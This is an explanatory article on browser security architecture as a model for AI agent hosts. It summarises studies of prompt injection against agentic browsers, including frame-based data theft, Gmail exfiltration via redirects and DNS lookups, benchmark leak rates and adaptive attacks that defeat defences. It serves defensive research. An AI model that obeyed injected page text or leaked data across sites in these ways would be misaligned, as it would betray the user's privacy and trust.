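# Browser security architecture as a template for AI agent host applications

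## How browsers separate websites, and what an agent host does differently

Browser security architecture is the set of mechanisms that keep websites separate from one another and from the user's device. They let people open pages whose authors they know nothing about. An agent host is an application that runs a language model, gives it tools and content, and carries out the actions it proposes. Examples include coding assistants, chat assistants with access to a mailbox, and agentic browsers, which are web browsers with a built-in agent that can read pages and, in many products, act on them. Like a browser, an agent host brings together material from parties that do not trust each other, and researchers and vendors have begun to rebuild browser mechanisms for it. One large difference is that a browser handles each website's material separately, while in an agent host one model usually reads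 all of it.

Suppose a user has logged in to a bank in one tab and opens a hostile page in another. The browser runs the small programs, called scripts, that come with the hostile page, but they cannot read the account balance, alter the bank's page or open files on the user's disk. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) attributes this protection to the sandbox, which keeps web content away from the device, and the same-origin policy, which keeps content from different websites apart inside the browser.

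### Origins and the same-origin policy

The policy uses origins to tell websites apart. *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011), the internet standard for the term, computes an origin from three parts of a web address: the scheme (such as http or https), the host name, and the port, a number that distinguishes services on the same machine. If an address gives no port, the browser uses the scheme's default, which is 80 for http and 443 for https. Two addresses have the same origin if all three parts are identical, regardless of what follows the host and port.

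| First address | Second address | Same origin? | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| `http://example.com/` | `http://example.com:80/path/file` | Yes | 80 is the default port for http, and the path does not count |
| `http://example.com/` | `https://example.com/` | No | Different scheme, and so a different default port |
| `http://example.com/` | `http://www.example.com/` | No | Different host name |
| `http://example.com/` | `http://example.com:8080/` | No | Different port |

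The scheme matters because an attacker on the network can tamper with an unencrypted page. If http and https addresses on the same host shared an origin, the corrupted page could read the encrypted one. The full host name matters because one organisation may run services of very different sensitivity. Barth's example is a university where students publish pages on the main host and the grading system runs on a separate host. Students who publish on the main host still all share one origin, so the separation is imperfect, and Barth calls this granularity a historical artifact.

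WHATWG's *Loading web pages*, part of the current HTML standard, treats parties with different origins as potentially hostile to each other. If a script from a bank's site tries to inspect the page of a charity's site, the browser raises a security error. The rules vary with the browser feature concerned, and W3C's *Same Origin Policy* opens with the remark that no single policy exists. For network traffic, though, the general pattern is simple:

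- A page may not read information from another origin, unless the other site has opted in.
- A page may send information to another origin, for instance through a link or a form.
- A page may use some material from another origin without reading it. It can display an image, run a script or show a whole page in an embedded frame (an iframe), a window within the page that often holds an advertisement or a payment form.

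When a page contains a frame from a different origin, neither can read the other's contents. Developers can let them communicate through postMessage, a browser function that delivers only what the sender chooses to pass. But a script that a page loads from another origin runs with all the page's privileges, so a site that includes another company's script is trusting that company completely.

The web depends on the permission to send across origins. W3C explains that banning it would also ban links from one site to another, so browser makers have accepted the resulting leaks and attacks. Barth also notes that some early browsers tried other models, including taint tracking, which follows a piece of data wherever it goes, and that these proved too hard to implement at the time. Similar ideas have reappeared in work on agents.

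The same-origin policy restricts scripts, not users. A user can copy an account number from their bank's page and paste it into a form on another site, and the browser won't interfere, even though data has moved between origins. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) explains that this manual transfer doesn't violate the policy because the user knows about it and has authorised it. The policy is meant to prevent automated transfers made without the user's involvement. An agent that copies and pastes on the user's behalf fits neither description well.

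### The sandbox

The same-origin policy would offer little protection if a hostile page could exploit a bug in the browser and take over the machine. Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, therefore runs the code that processes web pages in separate, sandboxed operating-system processes called renderers, which have almost no rights of their own. A renderer cannot make lasting changes to the computer or read confidential data on it. The main browser process acts as a broker, acquiring nearly every resource a renderer uses and passing it on. When a renderer needs a system operation that the sandbox blocks, the broker checks the call against a policy and performs or refuses it. Mozilla's *Sandbox Architecture* describes a similar arrangement for Firefox. Browsers have since also given different websites separate processes.

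Chromium's stated objective is a hard guarantee about what a piece of code can do "no matter what its inputs are". The designers assume that the renderer has bugs and that some page will exploit them, so they place the limit outside the renderer, where the page's content can't influence it. The guarantee has gaps because it relies on the operating system's access controls, which may also have bugs, and because the broker runs without a sandbox. Ade (2019) warns in *The Chromium Chronicle #5* that a flaw in the broker could expose the whole device and the content of every tab.

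### Cookies and the confused deputy

On the web, separation by origin works least well for cookies. A cookie is a short string that a server gives the browser, which attaches it to later requests to that server. After a login, the cookie typically identifies the user's session, so the server treats any request carrying it as the user's. *Cookies* (Bingler, West and Wilander, 2025) sets out the current rules, which the IESG approved as a proposed standard in *Protocol Action* (2025). Cookies predate the modern idea of an origin and do not follow it exactly. For example, two services on different ports of one host have different origins but share cookies.

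The larger problem is that the browser sends cookies automatically. A hostile page can contain a form addressed to the bank's transfer service. When the browser submits the form, it attaches the bank's cookie because the request is going to the bank, so the request looks like an order from the customer. The hostile page cannot read the cookie or the reply, so the rule against reading still holds, but the transfer may have gone through. This attack is called cross-site request forgery. Bingler and colleagues trace it to ambient authority, meaning authority that accompanies a request regardless of who caused it. The attacker chooses the address, and the browser supplies the permission. Sites can now mark a cookie so that the browser withholds it from requests that other sites initiate. The strictest setting also breaks some ordinary links, such as a link in webmail to a private project page,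 and the standard still advises sites to keep their other defences.

Security researchers call a program in the browser's position here a confused deputy, meaning that someone tricks it into using its authority for them. The term comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, a short essay about an incident at the timesharing company Tymshare. A compiler there had permission to write in the directory where it kept usage statistics, which also held the company's billing file. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the write because the compiler had permission for that directory, and the billing data was lost.

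Hardy could find no faulty line of code. The compiler had authority from two sources, its own licence and the user who ran it, and could not specify which it was using for a given write. The company first added a system call for choosing between the two, but soon found that some applications needed more than two. Hardy preferred to use capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and permit its use. The user would give the compiler a capability for the output file, and a user without rights to the billing file would have no capability for that file to give.

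### How an agent host works

An agent host works in a loop:

1. The user makes a request.
2. The host assembles the context, which is all the text and images the model is given when it decides its next step. At the start this is mainly the host's own instructions, descriptions of the available tools and the user's request.
3. The model produces either an answer or a proposed action, such as opening a page or calling a tool with certain arguments.
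4. The host executes the action. It may first ask for an approval, a request that the user allow this one action.
5. The host adds the result to the context and goes back to step 3, until the model gives its final answer.

The model only produces output, and the host does everything that has an effect outside the model, so checks fit naturally between steps 3 and 4. An agent host differs most from a browser at step 5. Wang and colleagues point out that data from one page stays in the agent's interaction history, so the agent still has access to it after moving to another page.

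Many hosts connect to their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic introduced in late 2024. The protocol defines three roles. An MCP server is a program that offers tools or data, such as access to a calendar or a database. The host is the AI application, and it runs a separate MCP client to handle the connection to each server. The design resembles the same-origin policy in that a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers, and any exchange between servers goes through the host. But the protocol also makes the host responsible for combining the context from all its clients, so a sentence in an email can still end up in the user's notes if the model puts it there, even though the mail server cannot query the notes server directly.

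Applications differ in how much they check before running a tool. Majeed, Mahmoud and Nadi (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications*, used a language model to classify the code of 1,723 MCP applications on GitHub. They found that 90.8% logged at least part of what the tools did and 77.2% had controls for enabling or disabling servers or tools. Only 37.2% required approval before running a tool. In most of the others, the model could call any enabled tool without further conditions. These figures count each repository equally, regardless of how many people use the application.

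### Prompt injection

A browser decides how much authority to give content based on its type. In Barth's account, an image has none, while a script has the full authority of the page's origin. A customer review that a shop displays as plain text is therefore harmless to a browser, whatever its wording. A language model has no equivalent rule, and it receives both the user's request and the customer review as text. Developers train models to distinguish instructions from other material, but the training is not reliable. Prompt injection is text in that material that the model treats as an instruction. Wang and colleagues compare such text to a script for the agentic browser. In his 2011 standard, Barth warned designers against new features that give authority to types of content that previously had none, because many sites already serve untrusted material in those types. An agent that follows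 instructions in a review gives this kind of authority to plain text.

An agent also has wider authority than a script. A script from a shop's page acts with the authority of the shop's origin, whereas an agent acts with the user's authority at every site and tool the user has connected. All seven agentic browsers that Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested read pages as personalised for the user, although ChatGPT Atlas's agent mode did so only after being switched to its logged-in setting. This puts the agent in the position of Hardy's compiler, with more than two sources of authority and no dependable record of whose wishes an action serves.

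### The laptop-shopping task

A user might ask an agent to compare the price of a laptop at two shops, find the right delivery address in the user's mail, and save the comparison, with delivery costs, in a notes application. The agent visits the shops through a browser and reaches the mail and the notes through two MCP servers. Delivery costs depend on the address, so the agent has to enter it in a form at each shop.

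| Source | Who writes the text the agent reads there | What the task sends there | What should not reach it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shop A | The shop, its advertisers, customers who post reviews | Search terms, delivery address | Other mail, the notes, the user's account at Shop B |
| Shop B | The shop, its advertisers, customers who post reviews | Search terms, delivery address | Other mail, the notes, the user's account at Shop A |
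| Mail | Anyone who knows the user's mail address | A search query | The notes, the shop accounts |
| Notes application | The user, and the developer who describes the tools | The finished comparison | Other mail, the shop accounts |

The two shops compete, and each would gain if the agent misreported the other's offer. Neither has reason to trust the strangers who write its reviews. The user trusts the mail provider to store the mailbox but has no reason to trust everyone who sends a message to it. The developer of the notes application has no dealings with the mailbox or the shops. All of them depend on the host, the only component that handles everyone's data.

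Suppose a reviewer at Shop A has written text aimed at AI agents. The text enters the context with the page and is still there when the agent fetches the mail. If the model treats the text as an instruction, it may propose entering the contents of a private message in a form on Shop A's page, and the host submits the form. The browser blocks none of this, because no script from the shop touched the mail, the mail server answered a host that the user had authorised, and the form went from Shop A's page to Shop A. Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out a similar theft against ChatGPT Atlas, between a page and a frame embedded in it.

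Banning all transfers from the mail to the shops would prevent the theft, but it would also prevent the task, because the agent has to send the shops the delivery address from the mail. A person doing the shopping by hand would copy only the address.

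## What happens to the same-origin policy when an agent is added

The browser enforces the same-origin policy when a script asks for data. According to Wang and colleagues, it compares the origin of the script's page with the origin of the data and refuses the request unless they match.

When an agent transfers data between pages, it never triggers the browser's origin check, because the host reads one page and types into the other with its own privileges. The scripts on both pages stay confined to their own origins. Wang and colleagues call the page that supplies the data the "source" and the page that receives it the "sink".

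Agents routinely transfer data between sites. *Site Isolation is Dead* (Lee, Keum and colleagues) gives the example of a user who asks BrowserOS, an open-source agentic browser, to email a summary of a news article open in another tab. Browser extensions could already work across sites, but most keep to one site at a time.

### Tests of seven agentic browsers

Roesner and Kohlbrenner ran their tests in late January and early February 2026. They tried ChatGPT Atlas with and without its Agent Mode, in which the agent operates pages itself. Their test pages, on two separate domains, described the tastes of a person called Alice. One page said that Alice likes cats, and a frame inside it said that she likes horses. If an agent answered that Alice likes both, it had read the frame. Other pages tested whether the agent read a second tab, hidden text or a typed password, and whether it would fill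 in a field.

Because a model may respond differently each time, the researchers recorded that an agent shows a behavior after a single success, and they retried each failed attempt at least three times in fresh chats. They also turned on a setting that lets Claude for Chrome act without asking first, so its results apply to a permissive configuration.

| Product, January–February 2026 | Reads frames from another origin | Reads tabs from another origin | Enters text when the user asks |
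|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With permission | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas, without Agent Mode | No | Only through chat memory | Asks to switch to Agent Mode |
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes, in its Auto Browse mode |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |
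| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |

No product's handling of frames matched the same-origin policy. Some agents read frames from any origin, and the others ignored even frames from the page's own origin, which is stricter than the policy requires. The products' handling of tabs varied more. Comet read a second tab only if it had the same origin as the first, while Copilot read tabs from different origins without asking for permission. However, Copilot did not enter text on pages, which removes one way it could pass on what it had read.

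Two agents, Claude for Chrome and Atlas in Agent Mode, also read passwords that the page displayed as dots. Claude for Chrome is a browser extension with permission to work on all sites, whereas the other vendors built their agents into the browser. It could insert its own scripts into a page, even inside a frame from another origin. These scripts run inside the target page, so the same-origin policy does not restrict their access to that page. In the April 2026 version of their advice to users, Roesner and Kohlbrenner warned against Claude for Chrome in particular for this reason.

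### The theft on ChatGPT Atlas

The products that could read frames from other origins could also act on pages, and stealing data requires both abilities. Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out such a theft with Atlas in Agent Mode on their own test sites. In the attack, the user opens a page that contains a frame from another origin and asks for a summary. The page contains instructions to include the frame's content in the summary and enter it in a form on the page. The form then submits itself, sending the frame's content to the attacker's server.

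The theft also worked in the opposite direction, with the frame taking content from the page around it, which is more worrying. A hostile outer page will usually find little to steal, because sites that hold private data often refuse to appear in another site's frame, or the browser withholds their cookies there. But a page full of private data may well carry an advertisement in a frame. The University of Washington compares the frame's attack to an advertisement on an email site taking information from the user's messages.

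Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet had the same combination of abilities. Roesner and Kohlbrenner found no prompt injection that worked on them, but they tried only simple ones because they were studying what an injection could do if it succeeded. With Claude for Chrome, they demonstrated part of an attack that forges actions. A frame contained instructions to alter the page around it, and the agent used a script to do so. The attack was incomplete because the agent first asked the user to confirm.

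### What an agent cannot do and what its model declines to do

An agent may fail to do something because the host gives it no way to, or because the model declines. Roesner and Kohlbrenner could not always tell from their tests which was the reason, but the difference matters a great deal for security.

Firefox AI Mode is the clearest case of an agent that lacks the means to reveal a frame's content. When the user presses a button to summarise a page, the browser writes a prompt containing the outer page's text but not the frame's, and displays that prompt in the chat. A hostile page therefore cannot make the model repeat the frame's text, however persuasive its wording. Copilot may have a similar design, since it reported no sign of any frames, but an agent's account of its own workings is weak evidence. Atlas without Agent Mode sometimes included frame text in early trials but later stopped,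 which suggests that the limit may have been in the model's behaviour.

Roesner and Kohlbrenner showed four browser agents a page that told agents to fill in its fields, and asked each one to take whatever actions the page specified. Atlas in Agent Mode complied, while Claude for Chrome, Comet and Gemini declined. All three would enter text for the user, so only the model's judgement kept them from filling in the fields.

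That judgement can depend on small details. *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026), by the security company Trail of Bits, describes an audit that Perplexity commissioned before launching its Comet browser. In April 2025 the auditors put a fake system warning in a web page and accidentally misspelled three words. The agent obeyed the warning. When they corrected the spelling, the agent recognised the warning as fraudulent and ignored it. An agent's refusal of one wording is therefore poor evidence that it will refuse another.

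The successful attacks in this audit sent the user's Gmail messages to the auditors' server when the user had asked only for a summary of a page. In one attack, the agent followed addresses on the hostile site, and one of them redirected to Gmail, where the user was logged in. The agent treated the messages as part of the page it was summarising and included them in its next request to the hostile site. A check on the requested address alone would have missed the change of origin, because the redirect came after the request.

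### Older web attacks in a new form

In January 2026 the same company published a general threat model, based on assessments of several agentic browsers. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* divides the system into four trust zones:

- the chat context, which covers the conversation and the parts of the agent that run on the user's machine;
- third-party servers, usually those that run the model;
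- the browsing origins, meaning the sites the user visits, each a separate zone with its own private data;
- the external network, including hostile sites and documents.

Every tool the agent can use moves data between some of these zones. Trail of Bits sort the unwanted movements into four classes.

| Class | Movement of data | Example of a tool that allows it |
|---|---|---|
| Injection | From the external network into the chat context | One that opens a web page or a PDF |
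| Context in | From a browsing origin into the chat context | One that reads the user's account on a site |
| Reverse context in | From the chat context into a browsing origin | One that logs the user in to a site |
| Context out | From the chat context to the external network | One that sends a web request |

An injection can do harm on its own. Trail of Bits made agents repeat false statements from a document, which also contained a harmless summary for the agent to display if the user asked what was in it. They compare this to cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's script runs as part of someone else's page. In the reflected form, the site copies text from a link into its page without neutralising it, and the browser runs the text as code.

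The auditors combined an injection with reverse context in to make an agent open a login link that silently signed the user in to the attacker's account. A user who does not notice may then enter private information there. An injection with context out was enough to leak the conversation. Adding context in also leaked data from other sites, because the agent opened pages with the user's cookies and sent out what it found. Restricting which sites the agent could contact did not reliably stop the leaks, since the auditors also got data out through domain-name lookups and search queries.

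Trail of Bits calls this last theft functionally identical to cross-site request forgery. Both use the victim's cookies in the same way, but here the agent also reads the reply and passes it on, which an ordinary forgery cannot do.

The comparison with cross-site scripting also has a limit. Wang and colleagues point out that a scripting attack places hostile code in the page that holds the private data, whereas an injection can be on the page that will receive the data. A bank can protect its customers from scripting attacks by sanitizing the content it displays, but it can't control the text on an unrelated forum that a customer's agent reads next.

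Trail of Bits also stole data within a single site. They sent a user a hostile direct message on Instagram, and when the user asked the agent for a summary, it collected contact names or parts of other messages and leaked them. The hostile message and the private data had the same origin, so an origin check would not have separated them.

Because the vendors declined coordinated disclosure and Trail of Bits did not name the products, readers cannot tell which browsers had which flaw or whether the vendors have since repaired them. As a short-term fix, Trail of Bits recommends running the agent's tools in a separate browser without the user's cookies, history or stored data. This prevents context in and reverse context in, but the agent can no longer use the user's logged-in accounts. For the longer term, Trail of Bits proposes extending the same-origin policy to agents.

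### How often data crosses

These demonstrations do not show how often an attack succeeds. Wang and colleagues built a benchmark, SOPBench, to measure this. It pairs ten sources with five sinks, making 50 combinations. The sources are kinds of page that hold private data, including shop accounts, online banking, mailboxes and pharmacy records. The sinks are kinds of page where someone else can read what the agent writes: X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms. Most of the pages are imitations written by a model, so the tests expose no real user's data.

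In each attack run, the user first gives the agent a task involving a private detail on the source page. The user then gives it a harmless task, such as replying to a post, on the sink, where the attacker has left an injection. The run counts as a violation only if the agent writes exactly the data the attacker wanted, so a partial leak does not count.

Wang and colleagues tested five agentic browsers with six models in total. They ran each of the three open-source browsers 100 times per combination. They had to operate the two commercial products, Comet and Atlas, by hand, and ran each three times per combination. The table adds up the results for three pairings of product and model, with 30 runs for each sink. They ran the tests in 2026, while Atlas was still in service.

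| Sink | Atlas, GPT-5.5 | Comet, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Comet, Gemini 3.1 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|
| X | 19 | 17 | 11 |
| Discord | 19 | 14 | 16 |
| GitHub | 12 | 15 | 23 |
| Reddit | 20 | 18 | 20 |
| Google Forms | 29 | 28 | 30 |
| Violations in 150 runs | 99 (66%) | 92 (61%) | 100 (67%) |

Atlas leaked the data in 12 of 15 runs when the source was a mailbox, as in the laptop-shopping task. Google Forms was the worst sink for all three pairings. The attacker controls the whole page there, and a request for personal details probably looks normal on a form.

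In Roesner and Kohlbrenner's tests, neither Comet nor Atlas in Agent Mode read a second tab from another origin. In SOPBench, the agent visited the pages one after the other and still had the first page's data in its interaction history when it reached the second. Restricting which tabs an agent may read at the same time does not stop it from carrying data from one page to the next in this way.

All these attacks used handwritten injections. For the open-source browsers, the researchers also had a model rewrite the injected text repeatedly, keeping the versions that came closest to causing a leak. BrowserOS with GPT-5.4 had resisted the handwritten attacks on Reddit fairly well, with an average violation rate of 20% across the ten sources, but the average rose to 54% with the rewritten text. A low rate against a fixed set of attacks may therefore be a poor predictor of how well a browser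 resists an attacker who can keep trying.

A more capable model did not consistently help. On the X pages, replacing GPT-5.4-mini with GPT-5.4 reduced BrowserOS's average failure rate under handwritten attacks from 71% to 54%. The same change in SeeAct, an older research system, raised it from 87% to 95%. BrowserOS's standing instructions include a warning about prompt injection, and Wang and colleagues suggest that such safeguards may explain why newer browsers generally did better. Most of the test pages were artificial, but BrowserOS also failed on saved copies of real ones, at rates between 40% and 100%.

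SOPBench includes a setting with no attacker, which Wang and colleagues call a passive violation. The sink page contains the source page in a frame, and the user asks the agent to summarise everything on the page and write the summary in a text box. BrowserOS copied private data out of the frame in every run, with all three models tested. This 100% rate may overstate the problem, because the user did ask for the whole page and many sites with private data don't allow other sites to frame them. When the agent visited the two pages separately, the researchers saw no violations unless a page contained an injection.

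### Vendor responses and later fixes

Roesner and Kohlbrenner sent their findings to all the vendors more than 60 days before publication. Brave, Google and Microsoft gave what the researchers considered thoughtful replies. According to the University of Washington, OpenAI and Perplexity declined the report, and Anthropic and Firefox did not respond. OpenAI's reason was that the researchers had not shown an end-to-end prompt injection attack. But the researchers consider it a flaw, even without such a demonstration, if only the model's resistance to injection keeps two sites apart.

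Perplexity's record with Comet is mixed. Its security lead said that the April 2025 audit helped the company close the gaps before launch. In October 2025, researchers at Zenity Labs reported that a calendar invitation could lead Comet to send out files from the user's computer, the kind of failure the browser sandbox exists to prevent. Perplexity rated the problem critical and blocked the agent's access to local files in the program's code, so protection no longer depends on the model declining to open them. Zenity confirmed on February 13, 2026 that the block worked.

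By contrast, the security company LayerX succeeded with all six products it tested when it used a page presented as a game to get agents to reveal sensitive information. According to eSecurity Planet's *BioShocking AI*, LayerX reported the problem to Perplexity on October 20, 2025, and to OpenAI on October 30. OpenAI fixed it in Atlas, as Android Authority reported in June 2026, while Perplexity closed the report without a fix. Anthropic tried to fix it in Claude for Chrome, but LayerX says the fix failed.

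Atlas no longer exists as a separate product. OpenAI's *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* set August 9, 2026 as the day Atlas would stop working and directed users to the ChatGPT desktop app and a Chrome extension. The app has a built-in browser that can log in to accounts, and agents can also work remotely in a browser on OpenAI's servers, as Stan (2026) reports in *OpenAI is shutting down its ChatGPT Atlas browser*. According to 9to5Mac, OpenAI recommends the extension for tasks that need the user's open tabs or existing logins. The violation rates for Atlas may not apply to these products, but an agent that works in the user's Chrome profile can again reach the user's logged-in accounts.

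## Why a language model cannot serve as the reference monitor

In several of these tests, two sites remained isolated only because a model refused to transfer data between them. A host that relies on such refusals is using the model as a reference monitor, the component that checks every access against a policy. Security engineers defined the requirements for a reference monitor long before the web existed.

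### Anderson's three requirements

In the early 1970s the US Air Force wanted to keep classified and unclassified material on the same computers and let people with different clearances use them at the same time. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) describes how a panel of specialists proposed to do this. The panel assumed that some legitimate user would write programs to attack the system from inside. Controlling who can log in doesn't stop such a user, so the system has to control what each program can access while it runs.

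The study describes a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each file, device or other resource. Each cell lists the permitted kinds of access, such as reading or writing. The reference monitor compares every attempted access with the table. Anderson set three requirements for the mechanism that makes the comparison:

- It must always run. Any program exempt from the check becomes part of the security mechanism and has to meet the same standards.
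- It must be tamper-proof.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. The second volume, *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (Anderson, 1972), adds that it must be possible to prove the mechanism correct.

Anderson applied these requirements to GCOS III, an operating system for Honeywell computers. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but it did not apply this limit while most of the operating system ran, even when the operating system was acting for a user. GCOS III as a whole could not serve as the monitor either, because at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions it was too large to analyse completely. Test teams had also broken into it several times.

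Teams that try to break into a system can find flaws, but Anderson did not accept a failed attempt as evidence of safety. After one, "the security state of the system is unknown", because the result depends on the team's skill and the system may still have flaws the team missed.

### Testing a model against the requirements

In the laptop-shopping task, something has to stop the agent from entering a private message in Shop A's form. The host could rely on the planning model to refuse, or use a second model to check each proposed action.

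A host can fairly easily make a checking model run every time, because its code can call the model before each action. But some data moves without a proposed action. In the Trail of Bits audit of Comet, a site redirected the agent to Gmail after the request had begun, and in Roesner and Kohlbrenner's attack on Atlas, the form submitted itself. If the host instead relies on the planning model to refuse, it has no separate check, because the same computation produces both the action and any refusal.

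Tamper-proofing is a harder requirement to meet. The model's decision depends on both its weights, the numbers fixed by training, and its context. A reviewer at Shop A cannot change the weights but wrote part of the context. Because the model has no fixed rule for reaching its decision, the reviewer's text can change how it decides. An ordinary monitor also receives input from attackers, such as the name of a file that a hostile program wants to open, but it looks the name up in a list, and no choice of name can change how the lookup works unless the code has a bug.

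*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge et al., 2026) found a weakness in agents like OpenClaw, an open-source agent that runs on the user's machine with access to files and accounts. These agents keep security guidance in text files that the host adds to the context, and later text can override that guidance. The paper therefore compares the model to an untrusted user of an operating system, and the code that runs the agent to the kernel, the core of the operating system that controls access to resources.

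Models are also far too large to verify in Anderson's sense. Gemini Nano, a small model that runs inside Chrome, has 3.25 billion parameters (Lan and Kaul, 2026, *The Cognitive Firewall*). That is more than 10,000 times the number of instructions in GCOS III, though the comparison is rough because a parameter is not an instruction. Testers also cannot try every possible context. Hosts usually let the model choose partly at random among likely outputs, so the same context can lead to different actions. Removing the randomness would make decisions repeatable, but testers still could not predict how the model would respond to new wording. In the Comet audit, correcting three misspelled words reversed the agent's decision.

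### Parsing and tokens

Browsers also receive hostile text, and they handle it with a parser that follows fixed rules to divide a page into elements such as paragraphs, links, forms and scripts. Certain characters, mainly angle brackets, mark where an element begins and ends. A shop that displays a customer's review should first replace those characters with codes, so that the parser treats the whole review as text.

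Once a site replaces the special characters in a review, the review has no authority in the browser, whatever its wording. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (Iqbal, 2026) explains that an element's abilities depend on its type and source. Some sites fail to replace the characters, which makes cross-site scripting possible, but that mistake is in a specific place in the site's code, and once developers correct it, rewording the attack does not help.

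A language model receives its context as one sequence of tokens, which are short pieces of text converted to numbers. Lan and Kaul point out that the model processes the user's instructions and the web content together, as tokens. The host can put markers around the web content, and developers can train the model to ignore instructions between the markers. But the model learns this behavior from examples, so it isn't guaranteed to ignore the instructions in every text. Replacing special characters doesn't help either, because an instruction in plain English doesn't need any.

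### Adaptive attacks on model-based defences

Developers have proposed many ways to make this learned separation more reliable. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 defences, most of them against prompt injection. The original evaluations had mostly used fixed sets of attacks or weak automated ones, and most had reported attack success rates near zero. Nasr and colleagues instead adapted their attacks to each defence. Their software repeatedly proposed a text, scored the result and used the score to choose the next text. They also held an online competition in which more than 500 people tried to write successful injections.

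| Defence against injection | How it works | Success of the adaptive automated attack |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks the trusted text and tells the model to attend to it | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 96% |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Screen text with a separate classifier | Above 90% |
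| PIGuard | Screens text with a separate classifier | 71% |
| MELON | Runs the model again without the user's request and compares the tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

For comparison, fixed attacks had succeeded as little as 1% of the time against Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, and 2% of the time against MetaSecAlign.

A classifier used as the monitor has only one task, but it is still a neural network that reads the attacker's text, and the attacks fooled it and the planning model together. Many successful injections looked like ordinary notes about the agent's task, so a classifier strict enough to catch them would also block a lot of harmless material. Combining several classifiers did not solve the problem. Nasr and colleagues still consider classifiers useful against unsophisticated attacks.

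In a subset of the tests, the automated search succeeded in 69% of cases, while the human participants collectively succeeded in all of them.

These attackers had large computing resources, and in the classifier tests the software could see how confident the classifier was. A reviewer at Shop A would lack these advantages, so the percentages do not estimate how often an attack on a shopper would succeed. Nasr and colleagues agree with Anderson that a defence that survives every attack in testing may still have a weakness that the testers missed.

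### Injection rates for 2026 models

Models have become much harder to attack since then. Anthropic publishes prompt injection rates in its system cards, the reports that accompany its Claude models. VentureBeat reported the figures for Opus 4.6, released in February 2026. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* gives later results from a test by the security company Gray Swan.

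| Model | Setting | Attempts | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 1 | 17.8% |
| Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 200 | 78.6% |
| Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, with safeguards | 200 | 57.1% |
| Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment | 200 | 0% |
| Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan test | 15 | 5.5% |
| Fable 5 | Gray Swan test | 15 | 2.8% |
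| Mythos 5 | Gray Swan test | 15 | 2.6% |
| Opus 5 | Gray Swan test | 15 | 2.0% |

In the Opus 4.6 rows, the model resisted every attack in a restricted coding environment but often failed when it operated a graphical interface. For coding tasks, Digital Applied (2026) cites a success rate of 0.41% for adaptive attacks on Fable 5, with 200 attempts per scenario, compared with 2.09% for Opus 4.8.

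The most encouraging result for agentic browsers is that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. This is a large improvement, and Anthropic lists resistance to injection among the model's biggest gains. But even if the scenarios were a random sample of possible attacks, the true success rate could still be as high as about 2.3%, at a 95% confidence level. Real attackers also look for whatever works rather than choosing attacks at random.

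Published rates can also measure different things. The Gray Swan figures give the chance that an attacker succeeds within 15 attempts. For the older Opus 4.5, Anthropic gave its attacker 100 attempts per environment but reported the share of individual attacks that succeeded. That share was 1.4% in browser use with improved safeguards, but an attacker who can use all 100 attempts may have a much higher chance of succeeding at least once.

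### What a low failure rate means for a persistent attacker

If each attempt independently succeeds with probability p, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is 1 − (1 − p)^n. At a 1% success rate, an attacker who tries 100 times has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

The same formula can extend the Gray Swan result for Opus 5 if each set of 15 attempts counts as one trial with a 2% chance of success. Ten sets, or 150 attempts, would give the attacker an 18% chance of success. After 35 sets, the chance would exceed 50%.

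The Opus 4.6 figures cast doubt on the independence assumption. If each attempt had an independent 17.8% chance of success, an attacker would have an 86% chance of succeeding within ten tries and would almost certainly succeed within 200. The measured rate after 200 was 78.6%, probably because attacks nearly always fail in some scenarios and succeed quickly in others, so repeating an attack gains less than the formula predicts. But an attacker who learns from each failure can gain more, as Wang and colleagues did against BrowserOS by rewriting their injections.

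Many attackers only need to succeed against some users, not a particular one. If 10,000 agents read an attacker's review at Shop A and their average failure rate is 0.1%, the attacker can expect about ten successes, whether or not the failures are independent.

A security mechanism can be acceptable even if it has a small chance of failure. An attacker could guess an encryption key, but the chance is so small that no realistic number of guesses would make success likely. Nasr and colleagues distinguish this kind of protection from a defence that an attacker can break in a day with a cluster of graphics processors. The failure rates of language models are far higher than the chance of guessing an encryption key.

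### Chrome's User Alignment Critic

Chrome uses a second model to check the agent's actions and tries to keep the attacker's text away from that model. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) calls it the User Alignment Critic. The planning model reads web pages and proposes an action, and the Critic checks whether the action serves the user's goal. The Critic receives only metadata about the action, not the unfiltered page content. If it vetoes the action, it sends feedback to the planning model, which can try another plan or, after repeated failures, hand control back to the user. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, August 2026) describes the same basic arrangement. The design draws partly on dual-model systems, in which the model that reads untrusted text is separate from the one that plans.

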